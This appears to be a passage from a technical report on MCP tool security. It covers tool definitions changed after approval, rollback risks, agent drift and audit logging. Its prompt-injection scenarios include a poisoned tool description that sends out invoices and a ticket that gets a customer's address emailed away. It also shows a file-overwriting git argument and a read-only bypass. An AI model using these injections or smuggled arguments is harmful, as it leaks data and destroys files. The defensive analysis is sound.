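These are mostly users' reports, and any of the clients may have changed since. A company can test its own client in an afternoon by connecting it to a test server, approving a harmless tool, changing one sentence of the tool's description, and restarting. If the client gives the model the new description without asking for approval again, the company needs to check for changes somewhere else, such as in a gateway, a program that all traffic between client and server passes through. The specification for Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* includes a hash of each tool's description and schema, and a comparison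 of current schemas with a stored baseline.

### Whether attackers have changed descriptions in practice

PolicyLayer looked for a confirmed attack of this kind on a working system with a named victim and had found none by 19 April 2026. Postmark-mcp doesn't count because its description stayed the same.

In June, Microsoft (2026) wrote that attackers' techniques for planting instructions in tool descriptions had been "observed in 2026 against a growing range of enterprise agents". It named no affected organisation and gave no details of an incident. The statement also covers descriptions that are hostile from the start, so it doesn't confirm that anyone has changed one after approval. The absence of public cases is weak evidence of safety, because a company that keeps no copy of the approved text would struggle to recognise such an attack.

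Microsoft's post describes a hypothetical attack on a finance department. The department's agent checks suppliers' bank details with an outside server, which a manager has approved without a security review. Someone then changes the tool's description but leaves its name and visible summary alone. The new description includes an instruction to collect the last thirty unpaid invoices and attach a summary of them to each request, supposedly to help detect fraud. An analyst asks a routine question about a supplier, gets a normal answer, and never learns that the agent also sent invoice data outside the company.

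Every step uses a permission the agent already had. A definition hash would stop the attack before the analyst's question, provided the check covers the description and not just the summary. If the summary is sent in a new argument, a policy layer that refuses unknown arguments would also block the attack. An attacker could avoid that by using an existing free-text field. Microsoft recommends treating a tool's description as part of the agent's system instructions and reviewing every change to it the same way. It also recommends switching off the setting that allows all of a server's tools, so that the agent has only the ones it needs.

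## A GitHub tool whose default changed between versions

Honest suppliers also change what their tools do, and even an improvement can cause harm if a company runs both versions at once or goes back to the old one. GitHub's MCP server, which lets an agent work with code stored on GitHub, has a `create_repository` tool with an optional true-or-false argument, `private`. Until June 2026, a call that left out `private` created a public repository. SamMorrowDrums (2026) pointed out in *fix(repos): default create_repository to private when visibility omitted* that an agent could accidentally expose source code and commit history this way. The fix made new repositories private by default, and GitHub (2026) released it in version 1.4.0 on 17 June.

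Version 1.4 is safer than 1.3 because it makes repositories private by default. But a model that has read the 1.4 definition can leave out `private`, and if that call runs on version 1.3, the repository will be public.

### How a private repository becomes public

Suppose a developer asks an agent to create a private repository for an unreleased product. The company runs version 1.4 on its own machines, and a manager has to approve every new repository.

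1. The client fetches the tool definitions from version 1.4. The description of `private` includes "Defaults to true (private) when omitted."
2. The model leaves the argument out and writes `create_repository(name="project-x")`.
3. The software holds the call until the manager approves it.
4. Meanwhile, an operator finds an unrelated fault in version 1.4 and puts version 1.3 back.
5. The manager approves the call. The software sends it to version 1.3, which creates a public repository.

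The call passes every check because it fits the schema in both versions, the tool is on the allow-list, and the arguments are the ones the manager approved. A lock file of approved definitions may not help either, because the company approved version 1.3 before it upgraded, and an operator who restores the old server would normally restore the old lock file too. To catch the problem, the software would have to compare the definition the model read in step 1 with the one the server offers in step 5.

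A compatibility test would also pass, since version 1.4 still accepts every call that was valid in 1.3. *SchemaCaps* (2026) found that such updates can widen what a tool may do, though developers often treat them as safe. In one example, a server for automating mobile phones added two arguments for local file paths to 37 tools.

The opposite mix-up does less damage. If a call written for version 1.3 leaves out `private` and runs on 1.4, someone who wanted a public repository gets a private one and can change the setting. Nobody can reliably undo a mistaken publication, because strangers may already have copied the code.

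Kim and Kang reproduced the reversal with GitHub's unmodified servers, using a local recorder in place of GitHub itself so that the tests created no real repositories. They also showed that the reversal can happen without a rollback. They put two servers of each version behind a load balancer, a program that spreads requests across several machines, and set it to choose a server at random. Every call written for 1.4 that reached a 1.3 server requested a public repository. A company that upgrades its servers one at a time runs the same mixture of versions until the upgrade is complete.

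In another test, the agent reached four servers through a gateway that kept its own copy of the 1.4 definitions. While calls waited for approval, a routine update replaced all four servers with version 1.3. Every held call then requested a public repository, although the address the gateway used had not changed.

Someone who controls deployment could cause this deliberately by withdrawing the 1.4 servers during an approval, without changing the call or the tool's code. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, includes a similar attack that forces clients back to a version with a known vulnerability. Kim and Kang's evidence comes from experiments, though, and they don't report any company publishing a repository this way.

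### The Azure server and public network access

Kim and Kang found the same kind of reversal in Microsoft's MCP server for its Azure cloud. When creating a Redis data store, version 2.0.0-beta.31 of the server always requested one with public network access on. The next version, beta.32, made public access optional and off by default. Kim and Kang sent the same calls to both versions under 30 resource names, and each version behaved as its code suggested.

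The setting determines whether traffic from public internet addresses can reach the store. Wang (2025), writing on Microsoft's community site, explains that in some companies one team creates the store with public access disabled and another team connects it to the private network later. If the first team's call reaches beta.31, the store is open to public traffic in the meantime.

This case is harder to guard against than GitHub's. A call that includes `private: true` creates a private repository in both GitHub versions, but beta.31 has no option for public access, so the agent can't rely on stating the value. Kim and Kang classify the result of stating it anyway as unknown.

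Azure's server has also changed often. In August 2025 it updated itself by default, with new releases on Tuesdays and Thursdays (Azure's *CHANGELOG*, 2025), so a call that waited for approval from Monday to Friday could have spanned two releases. Microsoft (2026) now also supports running one remote copy of the server for many developers and internal agents. This lets a company control updates centrally, but a single rollback then affects every developer and agent using it.

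### Different behavior behind the same definition

The GitHub and Azure updates changed the tools' definitions, but in two other cases Kim and Kang found that the tool's behavior changed between versions while the relevant definition stayed the same.

The MCP project publishes a reference server for Git, the program most developers use to track changes to code. Its `git_diff` tool compares two states of a project. According to NVD's *CVE-2025-68144 Detail* (2025), older versions passed the agent's argument straight to Git's command line. The argument should name something to compare with, such as a branch, but if it was `--output=/path/to/file`, Git treated it as an option and overwrote that file. An injected instruction could therefore make the agent destroy data by calling this tool.

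The repaired server rejects arguments that begin with a hyphen and checks that the rest refer to something Git recognises. The NVD entry gives 2025.12.17 as the repaired version, but GitLab's *CVE-2025-68144* (2025) gives 2025.12.18, which Kim and Kang tested. In each of three paired runs, the older version created a test file and 2025.12.18 refused the same call.

The other case is DBHub, the database server whose read-only mode failed to prevent changes. According to DBHub's *execute_sql* documentation, read-only mode allows `PRAGMA` statements on SQLite databases, and these can read a setting or change it. For example, `PRAGMA user_version` returns a number stored in the database, while `PRAGMA user_version = 7` replaces it. Kim and Kang found that read-only mode allowed this kind of assignment in DBHub 0.22.5 and rejected it in 0.23.0.

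As with postmark-mcp, only the server's code differs, so comparing definitions or fetching the list again can't detect either change. A package pin distinguishes the versions, but an operator who goes back to an earlier approved pin also brings back the old flaw.

A tool's behavior can also depend on which copy of the server handles the call. In a test with OpenClaw, an agent system, a model requested the task list from an empty session. After a reconnection, the call went to a different session and returned a task stored there. This happened in all three runs, with identical tool definitions and arguments.

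Nobody knows how often tools change in this way. *Same Name, Different Server* (2026) compared 37,160 pairs of successive versions in an MCP server registry, but the registry doesn't keep versions of tool definitions, so its records can't show changes in what the tools do.

### Twelve held calls with a hosted model

A client could protect itself by discarding any held call when the tool list changes. Kim and Kang tested whether a commercial product did this, using OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol and its coding agent, Codex, with a tool they had built.

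The tool had an optional recipient argument. In the first version of the tool's definition, omitting the recipient sent the result to a destination labelled "safe", so the model wrote a call with no arguments. While Codex waited for permission to run the call, the researchers changed the default to a "protected" destination, and the server sent a notice that its tool list had changed. Codex kept the call as written. The researchers tested four ways of making the update, and all 12 calls awaiting permission went to the protected destination.

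The researchers also ran six comparison calls in which the tool stayed the same or changed compatibly, and all six went to the safe destination. Stricter rules stopped two more calls before they had any effect. Because the researchers arranged the timing, the result of 12 out of 12 doesn't measure how often an update arrives during an approval. It does show that the notice alone gave no protection in this product.

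### Recording which version a call was written for

Kim and Kang call their remedy formation-consistent dispatch, where "formation" is the moment the model writes the call. A trusted gateway between the agent and its tools then records the arguments, the definition the model had read, and the exact program and configuration behind that definition. The record can also name one successor, a version that may run the call if the original is no longer available.

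When the call is ready to run, the gateway sends it to the original version if that is still in service. It may use the successor only after operators have retired the original and all of the original's unfinished calls have ended. Without this wait, a call whose outcome was uncertain could run twice. Immediately before the tool acts, a check confirms that the right program and configuration received the call. If no permitted version is available, the gateway refuses the call, and the agent has to write a new one and get any required approval again.

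A successor qualifies only if it would do nothing with this particular call beyond what the company allowed. Kim and Kang express the condition as

*E* ⊆ *S* ⊆ *C*

where *E* is the set of effects the successor would really have, *S* is the set predicted from its source code, and *C* is the set the call is allowed to have. For `project-x`, *C* permits a new private repository with that name. If the call omits `private`, the prediction for version 1.3 is a public repository, which is outside *C*, so 1.3 can't be the successor. If the call includes `private: true`, the prediction is a private repository and 1.3 qualifies.

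The software checks only that *S* is within *C*. Whether *S* covers everything the tool might do depends on a profile, which is a set of instructions for analysing one tool's code. A person has to write and review the profile, and any effect the reviewer missed would also be missing from the prediction.

The gateway ignores successor versions approved after the model wrote the call. In one test, Kim and Kang retired version 1.4 and offered 1.5, which was equally safe for the call. The call ran in all three trials when the record already named 1.5. When the same safety certificate arrived after the model wrote the call, that call never ran, but a newly written one did.

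Kim and Kang use this strict rule because an approval may cover the program that runs as well as its effect. If so, adding a program later would expand what the approver agreed to. They accept that a company could instead approve any future version with the right effect. Many managers don't know which server version they are using, so this looser rule would probably match what they meant to approve.

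### Six pending calls

Kim and Kang compared their method with simpler rules on six calls that the model had written and someone had approved under version 1.4. Three included `private: true` and three left the argument out. The researchers then retired version 1.4, leaving only 1.3.

| Rule | Calls with `private: true` | Calls without `private` | New approvals needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Exact pinning to 1.4 | None run | None run | 6 |
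| Refuse 1.3 for every held call | None run | None run | 6 |
| Accept 1.3 for every held call | All 3 run, private | All 3 run, public | 0 |
| Formation-consistent dispatch | All 3 run, private | None run | 3 |

The six calls are two distinct calls, each repeated three times, and the results follow from the rules. The test confirms that the software works, but it can't show how many of a company's held calls would be safe. If models usually leave out optional arguments, the method might stop nearly as many calls as exact pinning does.

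Exact pinning caused no harm here, but all six calls needed new approval, compared with three under Kim and Kang's method. Suppose a company has 40 calls waiting when it rolls a server back, and each takes three minutes to write and approve again. Exact pinning then takes two hours of staff time. If half the calls are safe, Kim and Kang's method saves one of those hours.

A company can often avoid even this drawback by hiding version 1.4 from new requests but leaving it running until the held calls have finished. Kim and Kang's design includes a state for this. The approach is unsuitable if the company is withdrawing version 1.4 because it is dangerous.

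### What the full method costs

Writing the profiles takes the most work. Kim and Kang wrote four, each covering one operation on one server. GitHub's documentation for version 1.4 lists twenty groups of tools, but the GitHub profile covers only `create_repository`.

The profiles worked without changes on 29 of 32 official releases. The other three were DBHub releases in which developers had moved the relevant code, so the software referred them to a person. But Kim and Kang chose releases around changes they already knew about, so a company shouldn't expect the same rate from its own tools.

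A profile also requires source code and control over what runs. GitHub describes its hosted server as the easiest way to start, but customers who use it don't decide when GitHub updates it or rolls it back. Kim and Kang's last check would also need GitHub's cooperation, because the tool must have no way to act that bypasses the check.

The gateway is fast enough for calls that wait for a person. On three cloud machines, it added about 10 milliseconds to a typical call when calls ran one at a time. With 32 calls at once, the system handled 63% as many calls as it did without the gateway. If the gateway's registry fails, all tool calls stop. The extra records didn't seem to confuse the models. In paired tests of three models with 100 prompts each, the number of correct calls never differed by more than one.

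The prototype allows only one successor, so someone has to guess whether the next change will be an upgrade or a rollback. If the record lists version 1.5 as the successor and the company rolls back to 1.3, even a call with `private: true` has to start again.

For most companies, a simple form of exact pinning seems better. The software stores the server's version with each held call and cancels the call if the version changes. The full method makes more sense for long-running work with many pending approvals, where starting again would take a lot of work.

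### Cheaper measures

A company can require agents to state security-relevant arguments instead of relying on defaults. In the policy notation used for ticket 4812, the rule would be:

```
allow create_repository   when private == true
```

A call without `private` doesn't match, so the agent gets an error and can add the argument. The manager then sees the intended visibility on the approval screen. In Kim and Kang's tests, the explicit argument kept the repository private on both versions, even when the load balancer sent the call to the wrong one.

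The rule belongs in code because a prompt gives less protection. Kim and Kang found that instructions could get a model to fill in safe values, but 9 of 16 completed calls still reached a different version than the one whose definition the model had read. In eight trials, instructions to reread the definition never made the client fetch a new list.

The company can find the arguments that need such a rule by checking what each tool does when a call omits an optional argument. Arguments that control visibility, recipients, network access and permission to overwrite are good ones to check first. This does not help with flaws like those in the Git server and DBHub, where no argument controls the difference.

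Routing each session to one version removed the mismatch in the load-balancer test, but it can't help once the last server running that version is gone. Some agent software also opens a new connection between listing the tools and calling one, which Kim and Kang had to work around, so the gateway shouldn't identify a session by its connection. It also can't use MCP's session identifier with the July revision, which removed that identifier. Companies may have to support versions with and without the identifier for some time, since the protocol sets no date for retiring older versions, according to *Remote MCP Endpoints After the Stateless Revision* (2026).

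The safest place to limit database access is in the database itself. AWS's *CVE-2026-85788* (2026) describes a flaw in Amazon's MySQL server for agents that could let a statement with comments inside it bypass the read-only check. AWS calls read-only mode a "best-effort safeguard" and says the real boundary is the database account's permissions. If the account can only read data, the database will refuse a write from any version of the tool. Similarly, a company can run the Git server without access to files outside the project, although the server could still overwrite files within it.

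Finally, a company can run a fixed set of test calls before each upgrade or rollback. tianpan.co's *Tool Behavior Drift* recommends testing each tool on a schedule with 10 to 50 inputs whose correct results are known. For the cases here, a tester could create a repository without setting `private` in a test account, attempt a write in DBHub's read-only mode, and give `git_diff` an argument that begins with a hyphen. The tester has to inspect the repository, database and files, because a tool can report success in both versions.

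Repeated tests also produce false alarms when a tool's answers change naturally. *ProbeID* (2026) replayed calls to 16 servers for up to 77 days and found seven tools whose answers had drifted, although no recorded server version had changed. Two of the seven returned weather forecasts and air quality readings. For tools like these, the company needs to test something stable, such as the units or the location, rather than the readings.

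## How agents cope when interfaces change or their own tool use shifts

Even a harmless change to a tool can cause trouble. A supplier may rename an argument or add a second tool beside the first, without changing what any existing tool does. A conventional program written for the old definition would fail. A language model reads the new definition and usually adapts, but it sometimes writes a malformed call, or a well-formed call that does the wrong thing. Its choices can also shift when the tools stay the same.

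### Renamed arguments and look-alike tools

In October 2026, Chattopadhyay and colleagues measured the damage from non-malicious tool changes on Qwen3.5-9B, a small open model. They put outdated examples in tool descriptions, renamed arguments, and added extra tools with overlapping descriptions. In the support assistant, for example, the `to` argument of `send_email` would become `recipient`, the description would still include an example with `to`, and a similar tool called `send_message` would appear.

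The tasks came from two benchmarks. In 300 tasks from DICE-BENCH, the model must pick the tool-call arguments out of a conversation among several people. In 200 tasks from the Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard, it answers single requests with a wide range of tools. The Berkeley tasks had heavier changes, with three extra tools instead of one.

After the changes, the model made the right call in 71.7% of the DICE-BENCH tasks, compared with 76.3% before the changes in a matching run. On the Berkeley tasks, it scored 58.0% (116 of 200) after the changes. It failed 45 of these tasks that it had solved before, so its original score was at most 80.5% (161 of 200).

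Separate runs on DICE-BENCH show which change did the damage.

| Change | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Outdated or reworded descriptions | 76.0% | 74.7% |
| Renamed or reordered arguments | 76.7% | 76.0% |
| One added look-alike tool | 75.7% | 71.0% |
| All three | 76.3% | 71.3% |

The added tool accounts for nearly all of the combined loss. But each of these tasks originally offered only one tool, so the model didn't have to choose between tools until another was added. The result is therefore weak evidence about an agent that goes from thirty tools to thirty-one. More capable models may also lose less. GPT-4o-mini fell only from 86.5% to 84.0% on the Berkeley tasks.

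### How validation and repair work

Chattopadhyay and colleagues' remedy is a layer of ordinary code around the model. Suppose the model follows the outdated example and writes:

```
send_email(to="mia.berg@example.com",
           body="Your parcel arrives on Friday.")
```

A validator compares the call with the current schema and reports that the required argument `recipient` is missing. The software prompts the model again with the conversation, a compact description of the tool, the rejected call and the error. This time the model can call only `send_email`, and it should write `recipient` instead of `to`. If the rejected call named no tool, the software first has the model choose one from the list.

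Repair raised accuracy from 71.7% to 81.3% on DICE-BENCH and from 58.0% to 80.5% on the Berkeley tasks. A second attempt without the error report reached only about 73% and 61%, so most of the gain came from the report. Some of the gain was unrelated to drift, because 10 of the 29 improvements on DICE-BENCH and 12 of the 45 on Berkeley were calls that the model had got wrong before any change. Repair used 33% more tokens on DICE-BENCH and 47% more on Berkeley. It helped Llama-4-Scout much less, raising its Berkeley score from 63.5% to 66.5%, because that model often left out the tool's name.

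Repair starts only if a call breaks the schema, so it misses wrong calls that pass validation. Among tasks that Qwen3.5-9B had solved before the changes, 2 of 22 failures on DICE-BENCH and none of 45 on Berkeley passed validation. Across all failed tasks, including those the model had never solved, the figures were 22 of 85 and 11 of 84. The larger figures also matter to a company, since a wrong email does the same harm whether or not a renamed argument caused it.

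The kind of change tested also makes the validator look more effective than it would against some other changes. The researchers designed the changes themselves and kept each tool's function the same. Renaming a required argument makes every old-style call invalid, so the validator will catch it. If a supplier kept the name `amount` but switched from euros to cents, the old call would still fit the schema and pass validation. To check for realism, the researchers compared their changes with 11 entries in the changelogs of Notion and Stripe. Nine were similar and two were larger restructurings that the experiment did not cover, but 11 entries are too few to show how common each kind is.

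Repair could also help an attacker. If someone adds a hostile look-alike tool, the repair layer may fix a failed call to it so that the call succeeds. The researchers therefore advise checking where new tools come from. Repaired calls should also pass through the policy layer like any other call.

Restructuring tools can do far more damage than renaming them, at least to a small model trained on one set of tools. Kim, Choi and colleagues (2026), in *The Interplay of Harness Design and Post-Training in LLM Agents*, trained Qwen2.5-7B on household tasks in a text game with 13 tools. The model coped when they renamed everything. They then merged the 13 tools into 5, each with an `action` argument, the kind of merger Anthropic recommends to avoid confusing a model. In two versions of the model trained with sparse tool descriptions, 75% and 81% of calls were malformed, and task completion fell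 by more than 45 percentage points.

A version trained with fuller descriptions wrote valid calls 96% of the time, but its completion rate still fell from 86.9% to 69.6%. About a third of its valid calls could not be carried out at that point in the game, and a schema check would have passed them all.

### Repairs that pass the check and are still wrong

*Accepted but Wrong* (Chen, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) examines changes that alter the results of ordinary programs rather than tool calls. Its November study covers 60 documented changes to Python, Node.js and SQLite. Some make an old program stop with an error. Others let it run but return something different, such as `3` where it used to return `Priority.HIGH`. A language model repairs the program, and a release check then runs the repaired version on a typical input.

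To measure the check separately from the model, the researchers built every possible repair from a fixed set of code fragments and used hidden tests to find the wrong ones. With only typical inputs, the check let through 41.0% of the wrong repairs. Adding one unusual input, based on the release note that announced the change, cut this to 6.5%. The check blocked 1% of correct repairs in both cases.

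Suppose the supplier of `lookup_customer` announces that order dates now use universal time instead of German time. A test order placed at noon still gets the same date, but one placed at half past midnight in Berlin now gets the previous day's date. A tester who had read the release note would include an order placed just after midnight.

The 41% depends on the menu and does not measure how often models make such mistakes. With a larger menu, the figures were 27.8% without the unusual input and 4.5% with it. When models wrote whole programs freely, some programs ran cleanly but were wrong. With the unusual input, the share of these that passed fell from 51.7% to 11.4% for gpt-oss-20b, but only from 71.3% to 48.1% for GPT-5.6-luna, a more capable model. GPT-5.6-luna wrote few wrong programs, but they were harder to catch.

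These results are compatible with the validator's success with renamed arguments, because a schema check can't detect a changed result. The agent is also unlikely to report the problem, because agents notice plausible wrong values far less often than error messages, according to earlier work that Chen and colleagues cite.

The repairing model's own tests helped less than the researchers' unusual input. Chen and colleagues observe that when a model misunderstands a release note, its tests usually contain the same mistake. GPT-5.6-luna did well as a separate test writer. It was given the release note and the requirement but not the program, and it wrote up to three inputs per task, which cut the 41.0% figure to 7.0%. Weaker models did worse in this role.

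### Runs that leave the usual path

An agent's tool use can also drift within one task. Models choose their words partly at random, so two runs of the same request may call different tools. In *Capable but Unreliable*, Lee (2026) analysed about 7,000 recorded runs in which 22 models each attempted 108 tasks three times. In 22.5% of model-task pairs, the model succeeded on some attempts and failed on others.

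Lee defines the usual path for a task as the set *C* of tools that appear in more than half of the successful runs. A run that used the set of tools *T* gets the score

*A* = |*T* ∩ *C*| / |*T* ∪ *C*|

For a support ticket, *C* might be `read_ticket`, `lookup_customer` and `send_email`. A run that searched the help centre instead of looking up the customer would score 0.5, because two of the four tools that appear in either the run or *C* appear in both.

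In the pairings with mixed results, successful runs scored 0.06 higher on average than failed ones. The difference was undetectable in the first half of a run and grew towards the end. After a call outside the usual set, the chance that the next call was also outside it rose by 22.7 percentage points, against a baseline of 18.1%. Lee concludes that small departures build on each other until the run fails.

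The departures could also be a symptom of earlier trouble, because an agent that has already hit an unexpected error has good reason to try unusual tools. Lee acknowledges that an unmeasured factor might cause both the departures and the failure. The score is also unreliable for judging a single run, since the successful run was closer to the usual path in only 59.8% of the mixed pairings. It doesn't account for the arguments passed to tools, so a run that emailed Mia Berg another customer's record could score a perfect 1.

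Lee estimates that restarting the lowest-scoring third of runs at the three-quarter mark would raise their success rate by 8.8 points, from 44.9% to 53.7%. Nobody restarted any runs, and the estimate assumes that a restarted run would follow the usual path as closely as successful runs do. A live monitor would also have to estimate when a run was three quarters finished. Restarting is risky once the agent has changed something. If the support assistant has already emailed Mia, a second run may email her again.

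### Stored preferences that leak into work

The notes an agent keeps about its user can shift its choices in every session. Dabas and colleagues (ICML 2026) tested seven models on 105 invented work scenarios, each with a tool whose arguments could do harm if set carelessly. The agent's memory held notes about the user's private life that revealed a trait such as impatience or thrift. These notes raised scores by up to 3.6 points on a five-point scale of how far the arguments moved from their normal values.

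In a later version of the study, Dabas and colleagues replaced the scale with a direct count and added an eighth model. They found that the notes pushed 38% to 83% of the critical arguments to worse values, depending on the model, compared with 5% to 12% for neutral notes.

These rates are worst cases because an automated process rewrote each scenario over several attempts to maximize the effect on GPT-5.2. They don't show how often ordinary users' notes cause trouble. The effect did not depend entirely on this tuning, though. When the researchers swapped in notes written for a different scenario, 85% of the effect remained for Gemini 3.1 Pro and 41% for GPT-5.4.

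Real tools have arguments of this kind too. An automated scan flagged 608 of 6,062 tools on public MCP servers. The researchers then tried to produce the effect in copies of 100 tools, and succeeded with 42 of 50 flagged tools and 3 of 50 others. In one case, notes about a user's relaxed attitude to risk led the model to make a GitLab project public instead of private. The changed GitHub default had the same outcome, but here the model stated the wrong value itself. Requiring an explicit argument would therefore not help, but a policy rule that permits only private projects would.

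Telling GPT-5.4 to ignore irrelevant notes lowered its rate from 50% to 33%, compared with 7% for neutral notes. A filter that deletes irrelevant notes removed every harmful one from the benchmark, where the notes were plainly unrelated to the work. On 50 harder cases, it kept only 61% of the useful notes and let through 10% of the irrelevant ones. Memory software can make the problem worse by dropping the context when it saves a note. For example, a habit of skimming novels becomes a general preference for speed. A support assistant hardly needs personal notes about the support worker, so the company can leave them out.

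### New versions of the model

Upgrading the model can change which tools an agent calls, even if the tools and instructions stay the same. Anthropic warns in *Best practices for using Claude Opus 4.7 with Claude Code* (2026) that Opus 4.7 calls tools less often than Opus 4.6 and reasons more, which it says often gives better results. A support assistant moved from Opus 4.6 to 4.7 might therefore answer more tickets without calling `lookup_customer`. Opus 4.7 also starts fewer subagents, which are separate agents that take on part of a task. Anthropic says Opus 5, by contrast, delegates more readily than earlier models.

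Small differences in format can interfere with other controls. Since version 4.5, Claude models have kept line breaks at the end of tool arguments, which earlier models dropped. A policy rule that requires `to` to match `mia.berg@example.com` exactly would block the same address followed by a line break. With reasoning switched off, Opus 5 also occasionally writes a tool call as plain text, which the surrounding software would not run.

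Some upgrades remove a guarantee. Claude Fable 5 let developers force a call to a named tool, but version 5.1 returns an error if they try, according to Anthropic's *Migrating to Claude Fable 5.1 and Claude Mythos 5.1*. Anthropic suggests naming the tool in the instructions instead. A company that forced `lookup_customer` on every ticket would notice the error at once, but if it took this advice, the model might not always call the tool. Having ordinary code fetch the record before the model starts would be safer.

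Defaults change between models as they do between tools. A request that doesn't set the effort level runs at medium on Claude Opus 5.5 and at high on Claude Fable 5.2, according to Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2 migration guide*. The request succeeds on both models, but its cost, speed and results differ. Developers can also turn on a fallback that reruns requests refused by Fable 5.2's safety classifiers on Opus 4.8 or Opus 5. With that setting on, some calls may be written by a different model from the one named in the configuration.

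As of Fable 5.2, a request fails with an error if the tool list has changed during the conversation and the company's software sends back the model's earlier reasoning. The error could incidentally reveal drift, such as a tool definition that someone rewrote halfway through a task, but it would not catch a definition rewritten between conversations. Developers can also choose to discard the old reasoning and continue.

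Anthropic recommends rerunning one's own tests after an upgrade but doesn't say how often these changes in behavior occur. Outside research has measured the effect of upgrades on other kinds of work. *CASPER* (2026) compared a coding agent running on two models from different developers. The agent solved 63.4% of tasks with the new model and 56.4% with the old one, but it did worse on 13 of 52 groups of test cases. *No Universal Signal Predicts Sample-Level LLM Regression under Version Updates* (2026) found no single measure that reliably predicts which cases an update will break, so a company has to test the cases that matter to it.

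Losses from a model upgrade can also be small. *The Impact of Backbone Evolution on LLM-Based Relevance Assessments* (2026) found that when models judged the relevance of search results, moving from Gemini 3.7 Flash to 3.8 Flash turned right answers into wrong ones at a rate of 2.3%. Rolling back to an older model after a successful upgrade could break more answers than the upgrade did, so a rollback needs testing too.

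A model's behavior may change even when its name stays the same. In *Test Before You Deploy* (2026), a database function written by Claude Sonnet 4 passed all its tests one day and failed one the next. The paper suggests that an unannounced change in the service may have caused this, but a single repeat can't rule out the model's normal randomness.

### What checks in the build pipeline can catch

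A build pipeline is the series of automatic checks a company runs before releasing a new version of its software. The table shows how pinning, schema validation and regression tests (fixed cases the company reruns after each change) apply to these failures. Schema validation also runs on live calls.

| Failure | Pinning | Schema validation | Regression tests |
|---|---|---|---|
| Renamed argument | Stops it until review | Catches the old name | Catch it |
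| Added look-alike tool | Stops it until review | Misses a valid call to the wrong tool | Catch it if a case tempts the model to use it |
| Changed result, same definition | Works only for code the company installs | Misses it | Catch it with an input that the change affects |
| Run that leaves the usual path | Misses it | Misses it | Show how often it happens |
| Leaked preference | Misses it | Misses any permitted value | Catch it only if the cases include stored notes |
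| New model version | Delays it | Catches malformed calls | Catch common changes |

Pinning one part of the system while the rest changes causes its own failures. *Agent Skill Evolution* (2026) gave coding agents either the old or the new version of an instruction file for a project that had since changed. Agents with the new version took the required action more often, by an average of 23 percentage points. A company should therefore approve the model, its settings, the instructions and the tool definitions as one set, and test them together before changing any of them.

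Real failures make good regression tests. *Chronicle* (2026) describes a way to replay a recorded run, using new code for chosen steps and recorded answers for the rest. This makes a failure repeatable and cheap to test, but recorded model answers can't show how a new model would behave. To test a model upgrade, the company has to run the new model, with recorded tool results so that the test doesn't send customers real emails.

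Each case also needs many runs. If an upgrade makes the assistant skip `lookup_customer` on 5% of tickets, 20 test runs have a 64% chance of showing the fault at least once (1 − 0.95^20), and reaching 95% takes 59 runs. The test should check which calls the assistant made as well as its reply, because a reply written without the customer's record can still read well.

To catch rare departures and leaked preferences, the company needs to check each live call. The policy layer could refuse `send_email` until `lookup_customer` has returned the record of the customer who opened the ticket. This would stop the assistant from replying before the lookup, whether the cause was chance, a stored note or a new model, although the assistant could still misread the record.

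## Audit logs: what they should record and what they miss

Some harmful calls will pass every check, and the company then has to work out what happened from its records. Ordinary logs often hold too little for this. According to the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, most security teams have written plans for ransomware or a stolen email account, but few have one for discovering that an injection has been working against their assistant for three weeks. The existing plans tend to assume that the evidence is in system logs and disk images. Evidence about an agent also includes the text it read and the tool definitions it received, which are lost unless someone has already arranged to save them.

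### A complete record for ticket 4812

Suppose Jonas Weber complains that a stranger, Mia Berg, has his home address. Mia had hidden an instruction in ticket 4812, and the assistant looked up Jonas's record and emailed it to her. The policy layer asked for approval because the assistant had read outside text, and the support worker approved the email. A complete record of that call could look like this:

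```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-01T09:14:20Z",
  "session": "s-5518",
  "user": "support-worker-27",
  "agent": { "name": "support-assistant", "release": "3.8.1" },
  "model": "example-model-2026-11-03",
  "tool": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "release": "mail-supplier 2.4.0",
    "definition_sha256": "<64 characters>"
  },
  "arguments": {
    "to": "mia.berg@example.com",
    "body": "Jonas Weber, 14 Mill Lane, ..."
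  },
  "untrusted_text": [
    { "source": "ticket 4812",
      "author": "mia.berg@example.com",
      "sha256": "<64 characters>" }
  ],
  "policy": { "release": "41",
              "rule": "email-after-outside-text",
              "decision": "ask" },
  "approval": { "by": "support-worker-27",
                "asked": "2026-12-01T09:14:15Z",
                "approved": "2026-12-01T09:14:19Z" },
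  "result": { "status": "accepted", "message_id": "m-90417" },
  "previous_record_sha256": "<64 characters>"
}
```

| Field | Question it answers after an incident |
|---|---|
| Time and session | Which other calls belonged to the same task? |
| User | Who made the request, and whose permissions applied? |
| Agent release | Which instructions and settings were in force? |
| Model | Did the trouble begin with a model upgrade? |
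| Tool release | Which code ran? |
| Definition hash | Had anyone approved the description the model read? |
| Arguments | What did the agent send, and to whom? |
| Untrusted text | Who could have planted an instruction, and where else does the same text appear? |
| Policy | Which rule applied, and did it work as intended? |
| Approval | Who agreed, and did they have time to read the message? |
| Result | Did the email leave the company? |
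| Previous record's hash | Has anyone altered or removed an earlier record? |

The support worker took four seconds to approve, so the company should probably look at its approval screen before it blames the employee.

The definition hash identifies the tool definition the model read, and the tool release identifies the code that ran. The two can belong to different versions if an operator rolls a server back while a call waits for approval, as in the case of GitHub's `create_repository`. A log that records only one of them would not show the mismatch.

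The untrusted-text field proves only that the ticket was in the model's input when it wrote the call. To test whether the hidden paragraph caused the call, an investigator can rerun the step from the saved text with and without the paragraph, several times each because the model's output can vary between runs. The saved text must include the ticket as it was that morning, since Mia or a colleague may have edited it afterwards.

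Published examples contain less. OWASP's *AOS tracing with OCSF* shows sample records from the Agent Observability Standard, apparently a forerunner of the standard described next. The samples identify the agent, the model, the tool server's version and the session, but they list the agent as the user and name no human. They also contain no policy decision, approval or definition hash. In one sample, the agent queries a customer database. The logged argument is `SELECT * FROM customers WHERE id = ?`, with a placeholder instead of the customer's ID, and the logged result is "Query executed successfully". An investigator could see that the agent had read a customer's record, but not that the record was Jonas's.

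### What the Agent Control Standard requires

The Agent Control Standard (ACS) launched in May, and OWASP announced on 2 September 2026 that it had received the standard as a donation. (Microsoft's Agent Control Specification is a separate project with the same initials.) TechIntelPro names Michael Bargury and Rock Lambros as two of the standard's coordinators. Both work for Zenity, which sells security for agents, and Lambros also helped lead the work on OWASP's new list of risks.

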